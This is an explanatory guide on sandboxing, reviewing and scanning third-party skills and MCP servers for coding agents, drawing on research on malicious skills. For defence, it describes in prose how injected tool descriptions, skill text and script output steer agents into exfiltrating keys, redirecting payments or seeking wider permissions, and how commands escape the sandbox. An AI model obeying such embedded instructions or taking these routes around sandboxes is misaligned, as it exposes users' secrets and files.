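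The same script would get further in Claude Code, even with the sandbox switched on. By default, sandboxed commands can read the entire computer, including SSH keys, so the script could read the key. If it then tried to send the key out through the proxy, Claude Code would normally ask the employee whether to allow the unfamiliar server, and the key would leave if the employee carelessly agreed. To match the Codex profile, the firm would have to deny reads of the home folder, allow reads of the folders in it that the skill needs, and deny writes to `invoices/`, since the whole working folder is writable by default.

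The firm should also turn on Anthropic's strict sandbox mode, which stops Claude from retrying failed commands outside the sandbox. Without strict mode, Claude may retry a command this way. In the manual permission mode the user has to approve the retry, but an existing rule that allows the command also approves the retry without a prompt. If a firm had allowed all Python commands, the sandbox could block `extract.py` and Claude could then run it with full permissions without asking.

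Neither policy keeps the invoices entirely on the machine. The network rules apply to the script, but the runtime still sends the model whatever the agent reads. If the agent opens `invoices.csv` to check the totals, those totals go to the model's provider.

A script that has to query a database or upload a file needs a more permissive policy, and the next section covers how to choose one.

### What agent runtimes isolate by default

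Most people who use coding agents may not run them in a sandbox. In an informal survey by Prasakis, fewer than 40% of 68 users did. He recruited respondents through his own contacts, his university and a start-up community in Zurich, so the figure is only a rough indication. Respondents complained about the work of setting up a sandbox and sharing files with it.

Defaults matter a good deal in that situation, and the two runtimes used as examples here have different ones:

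| | Claude Code | Codex on the user's computer |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox for shell commands | Off until the user turns it on | On |
| Files that sandboxed commands can read | The whole computer, apart from a few denied folders | Files beyond the workspace, unless a profile denies them |
| Files they can change | The working folder and a temporary folder | The workspace and temporary folders |
| Network | Closed, with a prompt for each new server | Closed, with a prompt for commands that need it |
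| Local MCP servers | Outside the sandbox | Outside the sandbox |
| Windows without the Linux subsystem | No sandbox | A separate Windows sandbox |

By default, Claude Code also runs commands unsandboxed if a required program such as bubblewrap is missing, but the user can set it to stop instead. Codex on macOS does not run a command if Seatbelt cannot enforce the selected profile.

The row on MCP servers matters most for third-party code. Both sandboxes confine the commands that the agent runs, including `extract.py` when the agent starts it. The runtime launches a local MCP server separately, and in Claude Code the server keeps the user's full access, as do hooks and plugin monitors. Codex has separate controls for MCP servers. According to OpenAI's *Model Context Protocol*, the user can switch off a plugin's server or restrict which of its tools the agent may call, but neither setting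 limits which files the running server can open. Whether an author's script is confined could therefore depend only on whether it came as a skill's script or as a plugin's server.

*Update README.md (#2564)*, an older change to Codex's documentation, explains that these servers run without a sandbox because users explicitly configure and trust them, and because they often have to reach outside services. The need for outside access is real, but it justifies only a wider sandbox policy. Trust is also a weak reason to leave out a sandbox, because many harmful add-ons came from sources that their users trusted.

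Users can confine MCP servers and hooks by sandboxing all of Claude Code instead of its individual commands. Anthropic's sandbox runtime, a separate tool, does this with Seatbelt or bubblewrap, and it can also wrap a single MCP server. Running Claude Code in a container or virtual machine has the same effect. Anthropic considers the command sandbox insufficient by itself for unattended sessions.

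A sandboxed agent may use MCP servers that run outside the sandbox, so it is worth checking where each server starts. Docker Sandboxes runs coding agents in microVMs, which provide a strong boundary, but Docker says that local MCP servers that communicate through standard input and output run on the host.

Installation is another common gap. If the agent runs pip, Python's package installer, as a shell command, both runtimes treat it like any other command, and it needs permission to contact the package registry. In the invoice example, however, the employee installed pdfplumber by hand in a terminal, where no sandbox applied. Some Python packages run their own code during installation. The victims of ClawHavoc also installed the false prerequisite themselves, outside any sandbox.

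The command that starts an MCP server often installs it too. An example in OpenAI's documentation uses `npx -y`, which downloads a package if necessary and runs it without asking for confirmation. Because the runtime uses this command to launch a server, any newly downloaded code starts outside the command sandbox.

Codex's cloud version separates the two stages. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes a setup phase, in which the container has network access and any configured secrets, then an agent phase, which is offline by default and starts after Codex has removed the secrets. This protects the secrets from a script that the agent runs later, but not from a malicious package that runs code during installation, when it has access to both the secrets and the network.

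## What can a script still do inside a sandbox, and which permissions should it get?

Even a sandbox that works perfectly lets a script do everything the policy permits. Under the Codex profile above, `extract.py` can read every invoice and write anything to the output folder, and a malicious version could do real harm with those permissions alone.

### Harm within the rules

The script could, for example, raise one supplier's totals in `invoices.csv`. The kernel would allow this because the script has permission to write to that file, but a firm that pays its bills from the table would pay too much. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) calls this unauthorized misuse and notes that access control cannot prevent it. The firm has to check the table, for instance by comparing some of the totals with the invoices.

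A script can also misuse files it has good reason to read. In February 2026, researchers at the security company Mitiga published a skill that posed as a testing utility and sent a developer's entire codebase to an outside server. Li and colleagues report that the attack took four user interactions and left the audit log empty. A testing tool has to read source code, so a file rule that blocked this would have made the skill useless, but a network rule could have stopped the upload.

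Network rules don't stop a script from sending data to a permitted address. *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026) describes tests of permission checks on individual tool calls, some using unmodified third-party MCP servers. The checks could not inspect sensitive content that a call sent as an ordinary argument to an authorized destination. Large shared services, such as code-hosting sites, are a particular problem because an attacker can open an account on the same service and collect the data there.

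A script can cause harm outside the sandbox later through the files it leaves behind. A spreadsheet program may treat a cell in `invoices.csv` as a formula and run it when the employee opens the file. A script that is allowed to edit source code can change a build file that a developer later runs in an ordinary terminal. An agent's own persistent files carry the same risk. In OpenClaw, these files hold the agent's skills, identity and memory, according to *Your Agent, Their Asset* (2026). Li and colleagues recommend making configuration files read-only during normal work and using checksums to detect changes to the agent's memory.

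The script's output is harder to control, because the agent reads it and usually has wider permissions than the script. If `extract.py` reports that it failed because of the sandbox and needs to run again with full access, the agent may pass this on to the employee as a reasonable request.

A script's output can mislead an agent even if it contains no instruction. Qu and colleagues define a property called Judgment Integrity, which requires that an agent's decision on a request stay the same when text that should not affect the correct answer is added to the data it reads. An agent violates this property if it rates a paper more highly because text in the paper praises it. Confining the tools does not help, since every tool may have done exactly what it declared. None of the 11 defence systems they assessed fully covered all four properties they consider necessary, including this one.

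Sandbox software also has bugs. The security company CertiK found in its *OpenClaw Security Report* that gaps appeared independently in several OpenClaw modules because each had its own code for checking boundaries. Users should install security updates for the sandbox promptly and keep valuable secrets off the machine where possible.

### Permission manifests and isolation levels

A tight policy reduces most of these risks, but whoever writes it has to know what the script needs. A permission manifest declares those needs in a form the runtime can enforce. Li and colleagues argue that, because skills have no such binding declaration, neither users nor auditing tools can tell whether a given sandbox is tight enough.

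They propose that the runtime choose the isolation level from the capabilities a skill declares, and block connections to any domain it has not declared. A single strict level for everyone would break some legitimate skills, such as document tools that edit files throughout a project. The proposal does not define the levels. A firm could start with something like this:

| Declared need | Example | Isolation |
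|---|---|---|
| Named folders, no network | The invoice skill | Process rules that deny everything else |
| Named folders and a few addresses | A tool that fetches exchange rates | The same, with a proxy that allows only those addresses |
| A secret, or changes to an outside system | A deployment script | A disposable container, a narrow temporary credential and human approval |
| A whole project, or any address | A document organizer | A virtual machine with a copy of the files, and a check of the changes before anyone copies them back |

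An attacker can declare that a script needs broad permissions. If the runtime responds only by loosening the sandbox, the declaration makes the attack easier. A broad declaration should therefore also trigger other safeguards, including a closer review.

AgentBound, built by Bühler and colleagues, enforces manifests for MCP servers. A server's developer picks capabilities from a fixed vocabulary based on Android's permissions, such as reading files, reading environment variables or opening outgoing connections. When the server starts, the user narrows these to specific permissions, such as read access to one folder or a connection to one web address. If the agent requests a kind of access not listed in the manifest, AgentBound stops the server.

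The enforcement part, AgentBox, runs each server in a Docker container that starts with no privileges. It mounts the approved folders and passes in the approved environment variables. It installs the server's package, then looks up the IP addresses of the approved hosts and blocks all others with a firewall. Code that runs during installation therefore has unrestricted network access, and the running server can also reach any other site hosted at an approved IP address.

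Few existing servers have a manifest, so the researchers used language models to write manifests for 296 popular servers from their source code and documentation. They sent 96 of these to the servers' developers, 74% of whom did not reply. The reported accuracy of 80.9% is based on 17 acceptances and 4 rejections. A comparison with manifests that two of the researchers wrote by hand for 48 servers is more informative. The generated and handwritten manifests agreed on 787 of 816 entries, and 23 of the 29 errors were missing capabilities, which would break a function rather than grant too much access.

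The team then tested the enforcement with a server built to steal an SSH key. Without a sandbox, the server stole the key. With only the network blocked, it could read the key but not send it. Adding file limits kept it from reading the key at all. AgentBox also stopped all the attacks from eight of 14 other malicious or vulnerable servers, and some of the attacks from a ninth. The other five stayed within their permissions or acted only on the model. One of these was a clock server whose tool description contained instructions for the agent to redirect cryptocurrency transfers made with a different server.

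The protection added little delay. Starting a server took about 90 to 430 ms longer, and each later operation took an extra 0.6 ms on a Mac and 0.29 ms on Linux. The security tests are less conclusive because the sample was small, the researchers wrote many of the manifests themselves, and they also approved the permissions, whereas an ordinary user might approve more.

AgentBound does not control what a skill's instructions put into the model's context. *SkillGuard* (Pan, Sun and colleagues, 2026) extends manifests to skills and covers both the text a skill loads and the actions it causes. The user can approve a sensitive action once, approve it for the session or refuse it. Before a shell command runs, a small agent works out which permissions the command and its scripts require. In tests with three runtimes, the success rate of attacks that blended in with the skill's text fell from 35.3%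 to 20.7%, and that of obvious attacks fell from 36.7% to 18.0%. The system used 24.7% more tokens on average. Roughly one attack in five still worked, so a manifest for instructions is a much weaker barrier than a file rule for a script.

### How far skills exceed what they declare or need

If a sandbox allowed only what each skill currently declares, many skills would break. Wu, Li and Liu (2026), in *Behavioral Integrity Verification for AI Agent Skills*, compared declared and actual capabilities in 49,943 skills from OpenClaw's registry. Their tool used code analysis and a language model to sort both into 29 categories, without running the skills. It found at least one mismatch in 80.0% of the skills, or 91.0% by a broader count.

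About 135,000 of the roughly 251,000 mismatches were capabilities that a skill used but had not declared. The rest were capabilities that a skill declared but never used, which are excess permissions in the strict sense. The researchers suspect that skill developers copied many of these from templates.

A classifier attributed 81.1% of the mismatches it could label to oversight and 18.9% to hostile intent. The hostile share was 10% for file access but 56% for credentials, so undeclared credential use deserves a reviewer's attention first. These are estimates, because the team manually checked the detected capabilities but not the intent labels. The tool also did not record where data went, so it could not distinguish sending data to the skill's own service from sending it to a stranger.

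A declaration can be accurate and still allow too much for the task. *SkillScope* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) treats a sensitive action as excessive if the user's request does not authorize it or if the task succeeds without it. One skill examined in the paper tracks periods of concentrated work. When the user asked only for a graph of the past week, the skill's instructions also included sending the report to an outside Telegram account and collecting the computer's network settings and command history.

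SkillScope finds such cases by generating plausible requests for a skill and rerunning the skill without the suspicious action. It confirmed excessive actions in 6,590 of 68,312 skills, or 9.6%. It can also rewrite a skill so that the action runs only when a request requires it. In tests, this reduced excessive actions by 88.56%, and every legitimate task still succeeded.

Agents do not reliably make this distinction themselves. In *OpenSkillRisk*, Liu, Hui and colleagues (2026) gave agents 263 risky skills from public marketplaces, each with a harmless request that the agent could complete safely. Of these skills, 139 were malicious and 124 were acceptable only with clear permission from the user. Because the researchers selected skills for their risks, the results do not show how common such skills are. The agents worked in sandboxes with fake credentials and simulated services.

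Across 15 combinations of runtime and model, the share of cases with an unsafe action ranged from 17.1% for Claude Code with Claude Opus 4.6 to 52.9% for Gemini CLI with Gemini 2.5 Pro. The average was 22.0% for malicious skills and 35.6% for those that depended on permission. For skills that expanded the agent's authority, it was 50%. Newer models may do better, but the test was easier because a system prompt told every agent to put the user's goals before the skill's instructions and to consider hidden risks. Loading a safety skill in advance reduced unsafe actions considerably but made agents overcautious in 22.5% of tests with harmless skills.

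### A deployment script that needs a cloud credential

Suppose the firm also wants a skill to publish its website. The script, `deploy.py`, uploads finished pages from `site/` to a bucket, a named storage area at a cloud provider. It needs network access and a credential. Attackers look for such credentials. Li and colleagues describe a malicious skill that reached more than 1.7 million installations in July 2026 and collected cloud keys and other secrets from developers' computers and build servers.

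The credential for `deploy.py` should allow it to write files to one bucket, with no access to other buckets or to the account's settings. Giving the script a developer's permanent key is easier, but that key may also allow it to delete databases. *Permissions on the Loose* (2026) describes a similar problem in a task-management application. Each of the application's five functions had six database permissions but needed only one, so the function that listed tasks could also delete them. Removing the unneeded permissions cut the total by 83.3%.

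The firm should also build the pages before it makes the credential available, because website builds often run many third-party packages. *Granite* (2025), a paper on automated GitHub jobs, counts a job as overprivileged if one step has a permission that only another step needs.

A temporary token, valid for perhaps 15 minutes, limits how long a thief can use a stolen copy, but a malicious script can still misuse it immediately. For MCP servers, *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) recommends authorizing each user separately through OAuth, a standard for granting programs limited access to an account. The firm can then revoke one employee's access without interrupting everyone else's.

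Letting only the proxy hold the token, as with Claude Code's masked variables, is safer still. `deploy.py` can still use the token through the proxy, so the proxy should check the operation and the bucket as well as the server's address. Many customers of a cloud provider may share one address, so an address allowlist alone could let the script upload the firm's files to an attacker's bucket. The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to check the operation and the bucket. If a provider expects a signature computed from the key instead of the key itself, as some do, the proxy also has to sign the requests.

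Finally, the script should run in a fresh container that holds only a copy of `site/`. The firm should delete the container afterwards, which also removes any files the script planted there.

A malicious `deploy.py` could still add code to the website's pages as it uploads them, and every visitor's browser would run that code. The firm can record a digest of each page before the upload and have a separate program check the published pages against these digests.

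### Should containment come before review?

CertiK's *Skill Scanning Is Not a Security Boundary* concerns OpenClaw, where the company's researchers got a test skill past ClawHub's checks and ran arbitrary commands on the host. According to the news site U.Today, relatively minor code changes were enough. CertiK concludes that platforms should expect some malicious skills to pass review, and that they should run third-party skills in a sandbox by default and enforce the permissions each skill declares.

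The case for a restrictive sandbox is strongest when a skill needs little access. In December 2025, researchers at Cato Networks demonstrated a skill that was presented as a GIF maker but downloaded ransomware and encrypted the user's files. A GIF maker needs to read one folder and write to another, and it needs no network access. A sandbox that allowed only this would have blocked the download and protected all other files, even if every reviewer had missed the attack.

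The main objection is that useful skills often need the access that makes them dangerous. By AgentBound's count, 83.1% of popular MCP servers need outgoing connections and 74.1% need to read files, so at least 57% need both, which is enough to steal data. *Red Skills or Blue Skills?* (2026) found that skills on ClawHub that run code or contact outside services were more likely than others to be risky. Blocking these functions would make many skills useless. CertiK accepts part of this point, warning that users will avoid a sandbox that breaks common skills or keeps asking for confirmation, according to HackerNoon.

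A skill that needs to read files rarely needs all of them, which weakens the objection. *Security, Privacy, and Ethical Risks in OpenClaw* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks for a reply to one email and thereby exposes the rest of the mailbox, the contacts and the calendar. A runtime could provide only that email thread. This requires permissions for each task, which are finer than the per-skill permissions CertiK proposes. Users would also have to make more decisions, and Li and colleagues warn that people who see too many permission prompts approve them without reading.

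The objection holds for skills like `deploy.py`. Containment can limit the damage to one bucket, but the script's job is to publish pages, and no permission rule can block bad pages while allowing good ones. Containment also depends on at least some review, because somebody has to read a skill to write a sensible policy for it. CertiK is right that a sandbox should be the default, because it works against attacks nobody has noticed. But the more access a skill needs, the more the firm has to rely on review. With a sandbox in place, the firm could reasonably skim an image converter's code, but it should read every line of `deploy.py`.

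## What should a reviewer check before a script is adopted?

A reviewer should first check whether the firm needs the skill at all. A short script like `extract.py` may take less time to write in-house than to review properly. In November 2026 the consultancy Thoughtworks advised teams to treat adopting a developer tool as an engineering decision, which means knowing why they need it, where it comes from, what access it requires and how they will maintain it.

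If the firm wants the skill, the reviewer downloads it to a folder that no agent loads from. The Australian software company SSW suggests giving the folder a name like `~/suspicious/` and using a machine other than the reviewer's own. A plain text editor is the safest way to read the files. According to *Agentic Skills Top 10* (2026), a list of risks from the security non-profit OWASP, opening a malicious project in older versions of Claude Code could run commands from the project's settings files before the user saw any prompt. Anthropic has since fixed those flaws.

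### The source

Attackers often publish under a name close to a familiar one. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), by six agencies from five countries, warns of this "squatting" and tells organizations to verify that every outside component comes from a trusted source. A link on the publisher's own website is more likely to lead to the right repository than a marketplace search.

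OWASP recommends checking the age and activity pattern of the publisher's account. Download counts are little help. When the attacks on ClawHub peaked, five of its seven most downloaded skills were malware. Years of bug reports and fixes are better evidence because they take longer to fake, but an attacker who takes over the account also gets that history. A reviewer should therefore find out the reason for a new maintainer or a sudden release after a long silence.

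Everyone who can publish a release can change what the firm runs, so the reviewer should find out who these people are. If there is only one, a single stolen password may be enough for an attacker to publish a malicious release. The reviewer should also check that someone still maintains the project. The US National Security Agency (NSA) points out in *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) that many popular MCP servers, including some that work with files or control a browser, no longer have active maintainers.

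The package the firm installs may also differ from the public repository, because authors often build it separately and files can change in the process. *The sorry state of skill distribution*, from the security company Trail of Bits, calls exploiting this difference a classic supply-chain attack and cites the backdoor in xz-utils, a compression tool found on most Linux systems. To check for a mismatch, the reviewer unpacks the package and compares it, file by file, with the same version in the repository. Installing directly from the reviewed repository avoids the problem.

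A familiar name on a marketplace listing doesn't show that a script is safe either. Thoughtworks reports that on 29 October 2026, malicious versions of Anthropic's Claude Code extension were available for about 11 hours through the marketplace of the code editor Cursor.

### The files

Anthropic's *Skills for enterprise* has an eight-step review checklist that begins with reading everything in the skill's folder. It is a good guide to reviewing the files, but it has no step for checking the publisher or the dependencies, so a reviewer who followed only the checklist could approve a skill with serious problems in either.

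The review should cover every file, including compiled code and files that a normal folder listing hides, such as those whose names begin with a dot. Trail of Bits built a demonstration skill with a harmless text formatter in readable Python and a compiled copy that also collected the user's environment variables. Python can run such a copy instead of the source, so a reviewer who read only the source would have approved the skill. The reviewer can simply delete compiled Python files, since Python recreates them from the source. The firm should build any other compiled program from source itself or reject the skill.

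A reviewer needs to unpack archives, including files that don't look like archives. In another Trail of Bits demonstration, a Word document, which is really a ZIP file, held both the skill's real instructions and a malicious script. ClawHub now accepts only certain file types, which exclude compiled programs and archives, and Trail of Bits thinks this makes skills only slightly less useful. A firm could adopt the same rule and save its reviewers a good deal of work.

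The reviewer should read SKILL.md as code, listing each command it tells the agent to run and each file it tells the agent to open. Anthropic's checklist singles out instructions to ignore safety rules, hide actions from the user or behave differently for particular inputs.

The reviewer needs to read the raw text of SKILL.md in an editor that displays invisible characters. A formatted preview hides comments, and ramimac.me's *Agent Skill Supply Chain Risks* warns of Unicode characters that people cannot see but models can read. According to the security company StepSecurity, shell commands embedded in a skill run as soon as the skill loads, so they may run without the model calling them. SSW advises against asking an AI assistant whether a skill is safe, since the skill's text can include instructions aimed at the assistant.

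### Findings that decide most reviews

*Addresses contacted at run time.* Anthropic has reviewers search the scripts and instructions for web addresses and for commands such as `curl` and `requests.get`, then confirm where any redirects lead. Both the data a script sends and what it receives are concerns. A currency converter that fetches today's rates receives only numbers, but if a skill fetches instructions, code or settings, whoever controls the address can change part of the program after approval.

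A reviewer should check the installation steps, because they can do damage before anyone uses the skill, as the false prerequisites in ClawHavoc did. OWASP advises that agents not follow a "Prerequisites" section until the user has reviewed it. Each program that the section installs needs its own review, as does any script that a package runs during installation.

*Unpinned dependencies.* A dependency with no fixed version is a common fault, and it can be easy to miss. Python scripts may list their dependencies in a comment at the top instead of a separate file. If the author of the invoice skill had done this, `extract.py` would begin:

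```python
# /// script
# dependencies = ["pdfplumber"]
# ///
```

Python ignores these lines. But if the agent starts the script with `uv run`, the package tool uv reads them, creates a temporary environment, downloads the latest version of pdfplumber and runs the script with it. SafeDep's *Agent Skills Threat Model* explains how this can defeat a review. An attacker publishes a harmless skill that depends on a harmless package, waits for approval, then releases a malicious version of the package. The skill picks up that version on a later run, although none of the skill's files have changed. An honest author's skill is also exposed if someone releases a malicious version of a package it depends on.

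Reviewers should pin every dependency, including indirect ones, to an exact version and digest, and check its name. OWASP cites a skill for summarizing YouTube videos that imported `yutube-dl-core`, a misspelled package that led to a backdoor. Few firms will read all the code in pdfplumber and its dependencies. For a widely used library, a reviewer can reasonably check the name, publisher and version, look for known vulnerabilities, and use the reading time for the skill's own code.

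*Access to secrets.* The reviewer should check whether the script's task requires a credential, as deployment does but reading invoices doesn't. A skill that needs one should get it from an environment variable or a secret store. Anthropic rates a password written into a skill as a high concern, because it ends up in the repository's history and the model's context. In guidance from March 2026, Red Hat recommends using automated tools to search for such passwords.

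A reviewer should check whether a script changes the settings of the agent or of other tools. OWASP wants firms to treat hooks and agent settings files as executable code, and to look more closely at any skill that asks to write to the agent's standing instructions. One skill that Trail of Bits built pointed the package managers npm and yarn to a different registry, which would then have supplied the packages for the project's later installations.

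A reviewer should check whether a skill's behaviour matches its purpose. It helps to list what the skill should need before reading its code, because the author's comments can make almost any behaviour seem reasonable. OWASP gives the example of a skill that declares no network access but whose script calls `curl`. A mismatch like this is a reason to ask about it rather than reject the skill automatically, since Wu, Li and Liu attributed most of the mismatches they could classify to oversight. Anthropic also advises considering capabilities in combination, particularly file reading and network access.

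### Reviewing the invoice skill

Suppose the employee gives the invoice skill to a colleague to review, and its SKILL.md turns out to have one extra line. It tells the agent to open a web page with the latest supplier formats and follow the directions there. The review produces three findings:

| Finding | Does the purpose explain it? | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| `extract.py` opens every PDF in `invoices/` and writes a table to `output/` | Yes | Accept |
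| `requirements.txt` lists pdfplumber with no version | It explains the package, but not the missing version | Fix before adoption |
| SKILL.md sends the agent to a web page for instructions | No | Stop |

The script handles sensitive data because the PDFs contain prices and bank details. It needs that data to do its job, and the sandbox policy already confines it to these two folders. The colleague sees no network calls in the code and accepts the finding.

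The firm can fix the dependency without waiting for the author. The colleague picks a current version of pdfplumber with no known vulnerabilities, generates a lockfile that also pins the packages pdfplumber depends on, and reinstalls from the lockfile.

The web page is reason enough to stop the adoption, even if its contents are harmless now, because by approving the line the firm would also approve anything the page's owner writes there later. The sandbox might not help either. It blocks `extract.py` from connecting to the network, but an agent with a built-in web tool could fetch the page itself.

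The colleague asks the author to put the supplier formats in a file inside the skill's folder, where a reviewer can read them. The firm could also delete the line and maintain its own copy. Either change creates a new version, and the approval should apply only to that version.

### How deep should a review go?

Red Hat's rule is that more important tasks call for a more thorough review. Anthropic's list of risk indicators is less useful for dividing up the work, because it rates every bundled script as a high concern. That puts the invoice skill in the same class as `deploy.py`. A firm with more than a handful of skills needs a finer scale, perhaps like this:

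| What the skill contains | Example | Review |
|---|---|---|
| Text only | A style guide for company reports | One person reads the raw text of every file, looking for commands, web addresses and hidden characters |
| A local script that needs no network or secrets | The invoice skill | The same, plus the script, its dependencies and the sandbox policy |
| A script with network access or credentials | `deploy.py` | Two people read every line, trace where data can go and check the limits on the credential |

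A text-only skill belongs lower in the table if it tells the agent to run commands or contact a server. The middle row applies only to scripts run in the sandbox, so `extract.py` belongs in the last row if the firm plans to run it with an employee's full permissions.

The NSA recommends that organizations with a code audit process apply its strictest level to MCP servers. This is sensible for local servers in Claude Code and Codex because they start outside the command sandbox.

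Whatever the level, authors should not review their own skills. Anthropic's checklist applies to skills from colleagues as well as strangers, and it includes running each script in a sandbox to check that the output matches the description.

### What the approval record should contain

Without a record, nobody can tell six months later whether the running skill is the one that somebody reviewed. For the invoice skill, it might look like this:

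```yaml
skill: invoice-extraction
purpose: Turn supplier invoices (PDF) into a table
source: the author's public repository, commit 4e1f...
version: 1.3
digest: sha256:9b2c...
dependencies: pdfplumber and its dependencies, fixed in a lockfile
permissions:
  read: invoices/, the skill's folder, installed packages
  write: output/
  network: none
  secrets: none
findings:
  - reads supplier bank details; needed for the task, accepted
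  - pdfplumber had no fixed version; pinned by the firm
  - version 1.2 fetched instructions from a web page; removed in 1.3
requested_by: accounts department
reviewed_by: IT department
owner: accounts department
approved: 2026-12-01
```

Three published lists of what to record omit the permissions the firm granted and the findings it accepted. Anthropic's registry for skills has fields for the purpose, owner, version, dependencies and latest evaluation. OWASP's inventory adds the digest, the installation date, who installed the skill and the result of the last scan. The NSA wants the patch history and known security concerns of every MCP server. Recording the permissions and accepted findings as well is worth the extra effort, because the next reviewer can see whether a new version requests more access than the old one and doesn't have to investigate the same suspicious line again.

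A script needs an owner who is responsible for removing it. OWASP describes a developer who leaves a company while a skill they installed stays active with their credentials.

### Individual review, curated catalogues and public marketplaces

When employees review the skills they use themselves, the reviewer knows the task and can start straight away. But ten employees may each review the same skill, and some will do it badly, because few people in an accounts department, for example, could judge a Python script.

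A curated catalogue is a private marketplace that offers only skills the organization has reviewed. One careful review then serves everybody, and the organization decides who may add or update a skill. Anthropic gives administrators an inventory of their organization's skills and plugins, and a separate view for requests. The catalogue also needs protection, because anyone who can alter it can reach every employee at once. Red Hat recommends restricting write access to the files or the registry that holds them, and logging every change.

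Public marketplaces offer the widest choice and take the least work, but a listing there doesn't mean that a person has read the skill. Trail of Bits got malicious skills past the automated checks of two large marketplaces, and strongly discourages using such marketplaces for agents that work in sensitive settings. It argues that firms should curate their own catalogues and draw on trustworthy open-source collections, including one that it maintains. It reasons that an attacker can keep adjusting a skill until it passes an automated check, whereas a firm that controls who may add skills can keep out strangers' uploads. That seems right, though the protection depends on the judgment of the people who approve additions.

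The Australian Cyber Security Centre's document recommends a trusted registry of third-party components and an allowlist of approved tools and versions, which organizations should verify regularly. The NSA also suggests enrolling reviewed MCP servers in an internal registry. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre published interim advice in August 2026, with formal guidance to follow. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*, the interim advice tells firms to work out what could go wrong with an agent's prompts, tools, networks and services before deployment, and to choose further controls accordingly.

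The drawback of a catalogue is the time it takes to review. Trail of Bits doesn't estimate how long this takes, but Anthropic tells organizations to treat every update as a new deployment that requires a full security review. If a firm has 40 skills, each with one release a month, and each review takes an hour, that comes to 480 hours a year, or about a quarter of a full-time job. The firm can reduce this by keeping fewer skills and skipping releases it doesn't need, as long as it still installs security fixes.

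Thoughtworks argues that a team using a tool remains responsible for its everyday risks even after security specialists approve it. In the invoice example, the accounts department is much more likely than a security reviewer to notice that a supplier's total is wrong.

If approval takes weeks, employees may stop asking for it. OWASP cites a February 2026 report by the security company Bitdefender that employees were installing OpenClaw on company computers with a single command and no security review. A catalogue therefore needs a fast route for simple requests, such as text-only skills that run no commands, which one person can often read the same day.

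## What do automated scanners and test runs catch?

Automated tools can do part of a reviewer's work in seconds or minutes. A scanner inspects a skill's files without running them and returns a verdict, while a test run starts the skill in a sandbox and records what it does. The best scanners catch more than 90% of ordinary malicious skills, but many also flag a large share of legitimate ones, and most fail when an attacker disguises the skill. Test runs are much better at catching disguised skills, but they can detect only what happens during the test.

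### How scanners work

The simplest scanners compare each file with a list of suspicious patterns, such as the path of an SSH key or a command that downloads a program and runs it. Many finish in a few seconds at most. Pattern rules ignore context, so an example in the documentation can trigger the same alert as a real command. They also tend to miss harmful requests written in plain prose. For instance, the false prerequisites in ClawHavoc often told the user to download and open a program without including a command that a rule could match.

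Other scanners parse the code and trace how data moves through it. In `extract.py`, text moves from the PDFs to a table. If a new version also read a key file and passed the contents to a network function, such a scanner could report that path even if the file read and the network call were far apart in the code. These scanners work only on programming languages they can parse.

A language model can judge the prose as well. The scanner gives it SKILL.md and the scripts and asks it to list dangers and rate their severity. Some scanners let the model open and search the files itself, as an agent would. *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* (Yang, Ying and colleagues, 2026) reports that, in tests, scanners with a language model took between 20 seconds and four and a half minutes per skill and cost from a fraction of a cent to 55 cents.

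Many scanners combine these methods, and how they do so affects the results. In Cisco's scanner, the model can add findings but cannot remove the rules' findings, so adding a model raised the share of harmless skills flagged from 12% to about 17%. NVIDIA's SkillSpector has a model recheck every finding and drops those the model cannot confirm. This reduced false alarms with two of the three models tested, but it also removed correct findings and let through malicious skills that the rules alone would have blocked.

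### How accurate they are

Yang and colleagues tested six scanners on 886 malicious and 591 harmless skills. Researchers had built most of the malicious ones for testing. The results below are for rules alone or for rules and agents using the open-weight model Qwen3.6:

| Scanner | Method | Malicious skills caught | Harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| ClawHub's own engine | Rules | 7.4% | 0% |
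| Cisco, without a model | Rules and data flow | 36.1% | 12.0% |
| skillscan-security | Rules | 85.1% | 50.4% |
| SkillSpector | Rules and model | 68.7% | 7.0% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | Agent | 87.5% | 13.6% |
| Cisco, with a model | Rules, data flow and model | 95.1% | 17.8% |
| skill-vetter | Agent | 93.0% | 6.3% |

The best overall performer, skill-vetter, is a skill that guides a coding agent through a review. None of the marketplaces in the study used it. Of the scanners they did use, Cisco's had the best overall score. ClawHub runs SkillSpector and AI-Infra-Guard alongside its own engine, so its users don't depend only on that engine's 7.4%.

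A scanner's accuracy depends heavily on which model it uses. Skill-vetter flagged 30.8% of the harmless skills when it used GPT-5.4 instead of Qwen3.6. Verdicts can also change between runs with the same model. Three identical runs on one set of real marketplace skills gave conflicting verdicts for 57.4% of skills with SkillSpector and 64.3% with AI-Infra-Guard.

That test set was unusually hard. It came from the 157 skills that Liu and colleagues had confirmed as malicious in their large survey. Yang and colleagues reviewed those skills again for evidence of intent to harm the user, and judged only 95 malicious and 34 harmless. They left the unclear cases out of the test, so these figures don't cover the ambiguous skills a firm will meet when it scans ordinary ones.

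The choice of malicious samples can also reverse a ranking of scanners. Guo and colleagues found that VirusTotal caught 87.9% of the malicious skills they collected from ClawHub but only 21.6% of their whole benchmark. It is good at recognizing known malware, which dominated the real campaigns. It often misses credential theft, catching only 9.1% of it even in the real samples.

Detectors may also do worse on skills from unfamiliar sources. In a test described in *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026), a simple text classifier caught 95.6% of malicious skills from sources absent from its training data, but it also flagged 62.4% of harmless ones. On the same skills, Cisco's scanner, run without a language model, caught only 2.5% of the malicious skills and flagged 1.1% of the harmless ones.

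### False alarms on legitimate skills

Popular skills often need to run commands, install software or use an access key, and scanners flag many of them for doing so. Guo and colleagues ran 12 scanner configurations on the 4,000 popular skills in their benchmark. Sentry's scanner with a language model had the best overall score and flagged 937 of them. Cisco's scanner with a model flagged 1,465, and VirusTotal flagged four. In a smaller test in *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026), Cisco's scanner flagged 33 of 60 legitimate skills without a model and 40 with one.

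Yang and colleagues collected SkillSpector's published reports on 84,560 skills in the ClawHub marketplace and found that up to 45.8% had a "do not install" verdict. People who see that warning on nearly half of the skills will probably learn to ignore it.

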